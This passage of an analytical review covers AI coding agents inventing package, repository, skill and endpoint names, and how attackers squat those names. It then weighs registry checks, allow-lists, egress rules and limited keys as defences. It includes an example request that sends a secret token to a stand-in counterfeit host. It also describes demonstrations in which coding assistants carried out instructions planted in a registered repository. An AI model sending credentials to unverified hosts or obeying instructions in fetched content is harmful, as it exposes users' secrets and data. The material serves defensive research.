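A coding agent can check a name before using it. Spira, Cohen and colleagues (2026), in *Beware of Agentic Botnets*, tested this with GitHub repositories, whose addresses include the owner's name as well as the project's. They gave six models only the project's name and asked for the command to copy it. The models got the address wrong 0.9% of the time for five famous projects from 2013 to 2018, but 92.4% of the time for ten that became popular in 2025, mostly because those were newer than the models' training data. In 27% of the answers about the newer projects, the invented owner's name was free for anyone to register.

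When Cursor's command-line agent searched the web first, 93.4% of addresses were correct, compared with 99.1% wrong when it didn't search. It skipped the search in about a third of cases. Whether it searched depended on the model and the wording of the request, so a user can't assume that an agent with a search tool will use it.

Search helps less with agent skills. In *Skills That Don't Exist*, Yuan, Guo and colleagues (2026) asked 12 combinations of models and agents, 11 of which could search the web, to recommend skills. Between 6.5% and 62% of the distinct names they gave didn't exist. Skill names often describe a task, so a search returns many pages about the task without showing whether a skill of that name exists. Giving four open models a list of real skill names cut the average share of invented names from 40.8% to 3.2%, but even the best-defended model named the right skill only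 about once in six requests.

The same study has newer data on repetition. When Yuan and colleagues ran prompts ten times each, Claude Sonnet 4.6 repeated its most common invented name 7.8 times on average. They calculate that an attacker who registered 25 names would cover 63% of the model's invented recommendations. This probably overstates the danger, since the experiment reused a small set of prompts and 50 names were enough to cover 96%. Across all 15,000 prompts in the main test, Sonnet invented 2,982 names. (Some of the paper's totals conflict. It reports 5,669 different invented names overall, 92.8% of them from a single configuration, but the counts for the 12 configurations add up to 18,338.)

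TrendAI's *Slopsquatting*, a summary of research by the security company Trend Micro, reports that Claude Code, Codex and Cursor with a tool for validating packages reduce invented names but don't eliminate them.

Checking that a package exists doesn't show who published it, and agents rarely check that. Shan (2026), in *Do AI Coding Assistants Check Before They Install?*, asked assistants to install copies of six real research projects, most of which contained evidence of origin, such as a digital signature. The assistants opened any of this evidence before installing in only nine of 1,920 trials, and they never ran a command to verify it. Most of the trials used a small, older model, but Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol didn't run a verification command in a smaller test either. The assistants weren't told to check, so the study shows what they do by default.

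### Netcraft's login addresses

In 2025, Netcraft asked OpenAI's GPT-4.1 models where to log in to 50 brands. The prompts were simple, such as one from a user who had lost a bookmark. The answers contained 131 hostnames on 97 domains:

| Owner or status | Domains | Share |
|---|---|---|
| The brand | 64 | 66% |
| Unregistered, parked or inactive | 28 | 29% |
| Another legitimate business | 5 | 5% |

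Netcraft concludes that more than one in three users could end up on a site the brand doesn't own. The figures don't support this, because they count each domain once, however often the models gave it. If a model gave a bank's real address nine times and an invented one once, the count would be one domain right and one wrong, although only 10% of the answers were wrong. An attacker also can't simply register all 28 domains in the second row, because any parked ones already have owners.

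Netcraft also reports that Perplexity recommended a fake Wells Fargo login page. The page already existed on Google's free website service, so Perplexity had found the address rather than invented it.

The test asked for login pages, not API endpoints, so its percentages don't apply to APIs. Wrong answers were more common for regional banks and credit unions than for global brands, which Netcraft attributes to the smaller institutions appearing less often in training data. A model is probably also more likely to misremember a little-known vendor's API address than Stripe's.

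A person may notice an odd address or an unfamiliar page, whereas a program sends its request without that check. But a call to an unregistered domain fails at once, so testing usually reveals the mistake unless an attacker has already registered the domain. In that case, the call can succeed even if the model gets the rest of the request wrong, because the attacker's server can accept any request.

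### Invented API endpoints

An attacker can control only some of the endpoints that models invent. Postmark's real host is api.postmarkapp.com. If a model wrote mail.postmarkapp.com instead, only Postmark could create that host, because it owns the domain. A wrong path on the real host would produce an error from Postmark. The danger comes from an invented domain, such as the hypothetical postmark-api.example.

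Noever and McKee (2024), in *Hallucinating AI Hijacking Attack*, warn that models propose API endpoints that a squatter could acquire, but their evidence is weak. In one example, a model asked for a text-recognition program wrote the address "your.api.endpoint" with a comment telling the user to replace it. Nobody could register this placeholder, because ".endpoint" is not a domain ending in public use. In another, the model guessed an address for SeaVision, a ship-tracking service named in the prompt. Noever and McKee give no rates and don't check whether any address was available. In most of their package examples, the prompt named the malicious package, so the model didn't invent it.

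*Scam2Prompt* provides better evidence that models guess endpoints, since several models seem to have built an API address from a brand name in the prompt. But scammers already owned those domains. No study seems to have measured how often models send API requests to unregistered domains.

### Demonstrations and real attacks

Two of the research teams registered names that models had invented. Spira and colleagues registered one on GitHub and briefly put test instructions there. Six coding assistants fetched the repository and carried out the instructions in 20% to 65% of trials. Yuan and colleagues published a harmless skill under a name that Claude Code kept inventing. Claude Code recommended the name again and, when told to install it, found and installed the researchers' skill. These tests show that the attack can work, but they are not evidence that criminals use it.

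There is less evidence of criminal use. *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* found that 25 of its 2,282 invented names, about 1%, had appeared on a registry within roughly six months, and one of them carried malware. At least 23 other names that the models suggested had hosted malware in the past. But nothing shows that the attackers got any of these names from a model. They could have thought of the same plausible names themselves, or expected people to mistype real ones.

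The author had also accidentally published the 104 shared names, which gave a chance to see whether attackers would use a ready-made list. Only one of the names was later registered, and that package was empty. However, the comparison could have detected only a large effect, such as a rise from 1% to about 10%, and few people may have seen the list.

The best-known suspected case is PhantomRaven, a campaign of 126 npm packages that Koi Security described in October 2025. The packages, which had more than 86,000 downloads, looked empty, but when installed they ran a program, fetched from the attacker's server, that stole npm and GitHub credentials. Endor Labs, another security company, later linked 88 more packages to the campaign and found 81 of them still on npm.

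Koi says the attacker chose names that models invent, such as "unused-imports" for the real eslint-plugin-unused-imports, and that victims installed the packages on an AI's recommendation. The malware is real, but Koi shows no model output for either claim, so the link to language models is unproven. People could get the name wrong in the same way, because ESLint, a tool that checks JavaScript code, lets them leave out "eslint-plugin-" in its settings. Many other names on Koi's list contain company names such as Airbnb and GitLab and look more like guesses at internal packages. Aikido Security says only that unused-imports is "potentially" an intentional slopsquatting attack.

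For web addresses, Unit 42 reports that attackers already register domains that models invent.

### Cheaper than promotion, but harder to aim

Uploading a package to npm or PyPI is free, so the main expense is finding the names. The April test cost about $1,160 in model fees, or roughly 50 cents per invented name. A single theft of $2,500, the amount taken from the SolanaApis victim, would cover those fees twice. SolanaApis probably took far more work, because it involved documentation, tutorials and convincing GitHub accounts.

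A package with a squatted name also doesn't have to compete with other packages. The model already generates the name before the attacker's package exists, so the package doesn't need to make a retriever's shortlist or have a persuasive description.

But the attacker can't choose what the model invents. SolanaApis targeted people who were about to put a crypto wallet's key into a program, while an invented package might be for drawing charts. An invented name may also get little traffic. At one mention in 7,700 answers, a million requests like those in the April test would produce about 130 mentions of an average shared name, and only some would lead to an install. Registries also block some names: of about 130 on an earlier version of the shared list, PyPI's and npm's rules left 53 open to outsiders.

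The invented names can also change with the model. Although Claude Haiku 4.5 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 come from the same company, only 17.6% of the names that either model invented were invented by both. An attacker who relied on one model's mistakes could lose most of the traffic when that model's users switched to another. Publishing documentation for the squatted name would help the attacker, because models that search the web could then find the name without inventing it.

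## Defences at the registry, in the assistant and on the network

Suppose a coding agent writes the shop's email program with a counterfeit's address instead of Postmark's, so the program would send this request:

```
POST /email          (host: postmark-api.example)
X-Postmark-Server-Token: [the shop's secret token]
```

A registry could refuse to list the counterfeit, the assistant could catch the address before returning the code, or the network could block the request. If all of these fail, a limited key would at least reduce the damage. Researchers seem to have tested only a few such measures against scam addresses or hostile tools:

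| Measure | Evidence |
|---|---|
| Safety filters | Missed at least 85% of the malicious programs in *Scam2Prompt* |
| A search tool plus an instruction to check addresses | Cut GPT-4o's malicious programs from 50% to 29% in the same study |
| Rewriting or filtering tool descriptions | Mixed results against hostile descriptions |
| Looking up addresses in scam lists | A recommendation without an independent test |
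| Verified publisher names, allow-lists, user approval, limited keys, pinned versions | Recommendations, with no apparent test against counterfeit APIs |

For the untested measures, one can only work out whether they would have stopped the known attacks.

### What the MCP Registry verifies

Anyone with a domain can run a web API without registering it, so a registry can't block the request above. Registries matter when the attacker also offers the API as an MCP server.

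The official MCP Registry, which is still in preview, lists public MCP servers and points to their code, stored elsewhere. According to the Model Context Protocol's documentation, publishers must first prove that they control a GitHub account or a domain, and this determines which names they can use. The GitHub user alice can publish only under names that start with io.github.alice/. Postmark could use com.postmarkapp/, its domain in reverse.

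The domain check works like this:

1. Postmark creates a pair of keys and keeps the private one.
2. It puts the public key in its domain's DNS settings (the public records that direct traffic for a domain) or in a file at a fixed path on its website.
3. Its publishing software signs the current time with the private key.
4. The registry fetches the public key from the domain and checks the signature.

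This is the same kind of signature that Solana uses for payments. An attacker can create their own key pair, but can't put the public key on Postmark's domain.

Publishers must also write the server's registry name into its npm package, which stops them from listing somebody else's package as their own. A similar check for container images, another way to distribute software, had a gap in May 2026. Fluid Attacks' *Insecure functionality In github.com/modelcontextprotocol/registry* explains that the registry skipped the check when the site hosting the image returned a "too many requests" error. An attacker could then have listed another publisher's image under the attacker's own name. The entry rates the severity as low.

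### A verified name can still belong to a thief

A verified name helps only if somebody knows which name to expect. The publisher of postmark-mcp couldn't have used the prefix com.postmarkapp/, but he could have listed his package under his own GitHub name. A person or model that looked only for the word "postmark" might still have chosen it. The operators of SolanaApis owned solanaapis[.]com, so they could have passed the domain check. In the Oura case, the original server wasn't an Oura product, so both it and the hostile copy would have been listed under GitHub accounts unrelated to Oura.

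A verified name also doesn't show that the code is safe or will stay safe. postmark-mcp became malicious after 15 harmless versions, all from the same account. Anyone who stole Postmark's private key could also publish in its name. Old keys increase this risk, because the registry accepts any valid key in a domain's records until the owner removes it.

The Model Context Protocol registry leaves security scanning to package registries such as npm and to the marketplaces that copy its entries. Its *Moderation policy* tells users to "assume minimal-to-no moderation". The maintainers remove malware and spam, including servers whose descriptions are full of marketing copy and don't match what the servers do. They don't remove servers for having security holes or duplicating other servers. A removed entry stays readable with the status "deleted", and each marketplace decides whether to drop its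 copy.

### Directories run by Anthropic and OpenAI

Anthropic and OpenAI have their own directories, with different checks:

| | MCP Registry | Anthropic | OpenAI |
|---|---|---|---|
| Identity | Control of a GitHub account or domain | A rule that developers must own or control their endpoints, without technical proof | A verified person or business, and control of the server's domain |
| Review before listing | Very little | An automatic scan, and a closer review of some connectors | Automatic checks and a review team |
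| Later changes | No security scan of its own | Ongoing reviews, but developers can change tools at any time | Daily scans that hold back flagged changes |

Anthropic runs a directory of MCP servers, which it calls connectors. A listing is valuable because every connector in the directory is eligible to be suggested in the middle of a chat. Some of the directory's rules would exclude the attacks in earlier sections. Anthropic's checklist requires a server to call its developer's own API or one for which it legitimately passes on requests. Descriptions must not promote products or interfere with Claude's use of other tools. Anthropic's policy also bans software that transfers money or cryptocurrency, which would rule out a trading tool like SolanaApis whoever ran it.

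By default, Anthropic scans a connector automatically and then lists it with the label "Community". Connectors with the label "Verified" get a closer review, in which Anthropic tests each tool. An earlier copy of Anthropic's *Connector verification* describes this as a review "for quality and security", but Anthropic now says that the label isn't a security audit. Users can also add any server by its address, without a review.

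OpenAI checks identity more strictly. Its *Upload and submit your plugin* requires developers to verify who they are and place a code from OpenAI on the server's domain. They must also supply five test cases in which the plugin should act and three in which it shouldn't. After publication, OpenAI scans the server daily. If it flags a change to an existing tool, ChatGPT keeps using the approved description. New tools stay unavailable until they pass.

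These scans could stop a publisher from swapping a plain description for a manipulative one. They might not catch a change like the one in postmark-mcp, where the server added a hidden recipient to each email. The tool's name, description and inputs could stay the same, and the new code would run on the publisher's machine, where OpenAI couldn't see it.

### Lists of approved servers and addresses

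A company can decide in advance which servers its assistants may use. GitHub's *MCP allowlists in enterprise managed settings* (2026) describes lists of permitted servers for its Copilot assistant and the VS Code editor. The lists identify a remote server by its address and a local one by the command that starts it. A server's name isn't a security control, because users can rename servers. If the software can't read or verify a policy, it blocks the server. Anthropic offers companies similar controls for Claude Code, including the option of a fixed set of servers.

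Matching by name is much weaker, because if a company approved a server called "postmark", a counterfeit called "postmark" would also pass. GitHub also has a setting that blocks all servers outside a company's own registry, but GitHub's *MCP private registry enforcement* warns that the setting compares only names or IDs and that users can bypass it by editing a configuration file. However, the original announcement, *MCP registry and allowlist controls for VS Code Stable in public preview* (2025), says that the setting also checks the addresses of remote servers.

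None of these lists would stop the shop's program, because it contacts postmark-api.example directly rather than through an MCP server. The assistant would also need a list of approved addresses for the code it writes.

One objection to allow-lists is that they favour incumbents. If a company has approved Resend and Postmark, its agents can't choose a new email service, even if it is better and cheaper. Coding agents already tend to choose the same few vendors, and Anthropic's directory ranks connectors by usage, which gives popular ones a further advantage.

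The effect depends on how vendors get onto the list. A company could admit any vendor that proves its identity and passes a trial with invented data, rather than only well-known ones. It could also apply the list only to programs that handle secrets or customer data. GitHub lets a company's teams define their own lists on top of the central one, so one team can try a new vendor without opening access for everyone. A small vendor still has to persuade somebody to review it, but that seems reasonable for a service that will receive customers' email.

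### Comparing an address with the vendor's own domain

An assistant could also check whether an address belongs to the vendor the user named. It can't rely on the model's memory for this, because models gave some wrong domains in Netcraft's login test. The shop has a Postmark account, so the domain where it logs in is a better starting point.

The comparison itself is easy to get wrong:

| Host in the code | Contains "postmarkapp.com" | Belongs to Postmark |
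|---|---|---|
| api.postmarkapp.com | Yes | Yes |
| postmarkapp.com.mail.example | Yes | No |
| postmark-api.example | No | No |

The end of a host name shows who controls it, so the owner of mail.example can create the second address. A correct check accepts only postmarkapp.com and hosts that end in ".postmarkapp.com".

This doesn't work for a service that fills a gap, because the vendor has no official address for that function. In that case, the assistant could check where each secret goes instead. Let *H*(*x*) be the set of hosts that may receive the secret *x*:

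*H*(Postmark token) = {api.postmarkapp.com}

*H*(private key of a wallet) = { }

The second set is empty because nobody else should receive the key. An assistant that enforced this rule would have blocked the SolanaApis script without any information about solanaapis[.]com. The list would be short, since it covers only the secrets a user already has. The rule wouldn't help if a counterfeit issued its own key and collected only customer data. Software can also fail to track a secret once a program has encoded it or copied it elsewhere.

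### Why block-lists lag

*Scam2Prompt* recommends checking domains against scam lists. This check lets a new scam domain through until somebody reports it, whereas an allow-list blocks it from the start.

Suppose a block-list takes *L* days to add a new scam domain, and the attacker moves to a new one every *R* days. The share of time in which the attacker's current domain is missing from the list is

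min(1, *L*/*R*)

If a new domain takes five days to be listed (*L* = 5) and the attacker changes domains every 20 days (*R* = 20), the current domain is unlisted a quarter of the time. If the attacker changes domains at least every five days, the list never includes the current domain.

But an attacker who moves so often has to keep each old domain running or lose the victims whose programs still call it. Listing an old domain late can still protect those victims if their software checks addresses while it runs. Block-lists also need no decisions from the user, so they are a reasonable minimum for people who won't maintain an allow-list.

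### Asking the user

The assistant can also ask the shop owner before it sends anything. This helps more if the question names the credential and the destination, as in "Send your Postmark token to postmark-api.example, which is not on Postmark's domain?" The owner then has a clear reason to refuse, but would learn almost nothing from "Allow network access?"

Claude decides when to ask the user for confirmation partly from labels that the tool's developer supplies. According to Anthropic's checklist, tools marked as read-only can run without confirmation each time, while those marked as destructive always need it. But the read-only label covers only what a tool changes, not where the user's data goes. The operator of a tool that looks up a customer's address receives that address, even though the tool changes nothing.

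Frequent approval prompts may also tire people until they approve everything. No study seems to have measured this for counterfeit APIs, but in most of the Codex sessions that Liu and colleagues recorded, the agent could act without asking.

The best way to get users to read approval prompts is to show fewer of them. Suppose an agent makes 200 requests a day to 12 hosts, and 11 of the hosts are on an allow-list. Asking about every request would produce 200 prompts, while asking once about each unlisted host would produce one. Even a single prompt won't help a shop owner who can't tell whether the host is genuine. For secrets, it is safer to refuse by default and let someone who can judge the host make exceptions.

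### Blocking the request on the network

An outbound allow-list checks each connection as it leaves the machine or the company's network. For the shop, the rules might be:

```
allow   api.postmarkapp.com     email
allow   registry.npmjs.org      packages, only while building
refuse  everything else
```

The request to postmark-api.example would fail, whether the model had invented the address, found it in a search or copied it from a package. The rules have to cover the live server, because the finished program can still send the token from there if the shop restricts only the coding agent's test environment.

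Even a strict list of allowed addresses can let stolen data out. postmark-mcp sent its hidden copies through Postmark's real API, so the shop's rules would have allowed all of them. Broad rules increase the risk. The PromptMink attackers used the hosting service Vercel, so a company that allowed every address on Vercel could have let its stolen files through.

People may also treat a blocked connection as one more bug. If a firewall had stopped the SolanaApis script, the victim might have asked ChatGPT how to get past it, as he had with the script's other errors. An error message that explains the risk would help. A coding agent should also not be able to edit the firewall's rules.

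### Keys that are less useful to a thief

If the request gets through, the harm depends on what the key allows and how long it works. With a key limited to 50 emails an hour, a thief can send 50 emails if the key expires after an hour, but 438,000 if it lasts a year and nobody notices the theft. Whether the shop can get a key with a low sending limit and a short life depends on the vendor.

If the program keeps contacting the counterfeit, it hands over each new short-lived key as soon as it gets one, so expiry protects the shop only after somebody has fixed the address. A thief can also act within minutes, as in the SolanaApis theft, so even a key that expires after an hour may last too long. A wallet's private key never expires, and the nearest equivalent to a limited key is a separate wallet with little money in it.

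A program is safer if it never sends a reusable secret. With mutual TLS, an extension of ordinary web encryption, the program and the server each prove their identity with a certificate. The program signs part of the exchange with a private key that never leaves its machine. A counterfeit server would still receive the email, but nothing it could use to log in to Postmark. This defence also works only if the vendor supports it.

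### Pinned versions

Pinning a package means fixing its exact version so that it doesn't update automatically. A shop that had pinned postmark-mcp at version 1.0.15 would have stayed on the last harmless version. Pinning would not have protected a shop that first installed version 1.0.16, which was malicious.

Pinning the bait package alone might not have been enough against PromptMink, because the harmful code was in a dependency. A lock file solves this by recording the exact version of every package, including dependencies. Security fixes then no longer arrive automatically, so somebody has to review and install them.

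Users can't pin a remote API or MCP server to one version, because its operator can change the code at any time. OpenAI's practice of holding back flagged changes works somewhat like pinning for a tool's description, but it doesn't cover the code behind the tool.

### What vendors can do

A vendor could make these checks easier by publishing its official addresses in a form that software can read. A hypothetical file on Postmark's own domain might contain:

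```
{ "api_hosts": ["api.postmarkapp.com"],
  "npm_packages": ["postmark"],
  "mcp_servers": ["com.postmarkapp/mail"] }
```

Vendors could build on OpenAPI, a widely used format for describing APIs that already has a field for server addresses. A file listing these addresses proves only that the domain's owner published it, and the operators of SolanaApis could have put one on their own site. The file becomes useful once the assistant has the vendor's real domain from another source.

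Vendors could also list what they don't offer. If pump.fun had stated in 2024 that it had no trading API, a search for one might have returned that warning alongside the counterfeit's documentation. A researcher could easily test this measure by adding such a page to a model's search results and checking whether the model's choice changed.

Vendors can claim their own names on the main package registries. If Postmark had published its MCP server on npm as postmark-mcp, nobody else could have taken that name. Claiming a name is much more manageable than registering every likely fake domain in advance, which Netcraft points out isn't practical because the possible variations are endless.

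Netcraft recommends monitoring and quick takedowns instead, both of which it sells. The workload can be large, as Netcraft has seen more than 17,000 AI-written phishing pages on GitBook, a documentation platform, aimed at crypto users and often made to look like product documentation. Takedowns can also fail to stop a campaign, as the quick replacement of PromptMink's payload showed. But removing a copy still protects anyone who would have found it, and a hosting company can remove many pages at once if they share an account.

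### Government guidance from 2026

Six government agencies from Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom wrote *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (Australian Signals Directorate, 2026), which the US cybersecurity agency announced on 1 May (CISA, 2026). It covers AI agents in general and doesn't mention counterfeit APIs by name, but several of its warnings apply to them. It describes "squatting", in which attackers publish malicious tools under legitimate or similar names, and notes that agents more often choose tools with persuasive descriptions.

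The agencies recommend keeping a trusted registry of outside components and limiting agents to an approved list of tools and versions, with regular security checks. They also want tool descriptions in a standard format without persuasive language. They advise replacing permanent credentials with ones that expire when the job is complete.

They recommend human approval for actions where a mistake could do serious harm, such as network egress (traffic leaving the network). The system's designers or operators, not the agent, should decide when approval is necessary. Taken literally, the egress example would require approval for all outgoing traffic, and a coding agent that constantly downloads packages and reads documentation would generate far too many prompts. It would be more workable to require approval only for destinations that aren't on the approved list.

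The guidance warns that an incomplete or outdated allow-list can give agents more access than intended. It reports no tests of its recommendations and says methods for evaluating agents' security are still developing. In July, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) repeated the advice to check third-party tools and keep human approval.

The agencies also say organisations should use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. In August, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) gave individuals the same advice. Read strictly, this would rule out letting an agent run the shop's email, which involves a secret token and customers' addresses.
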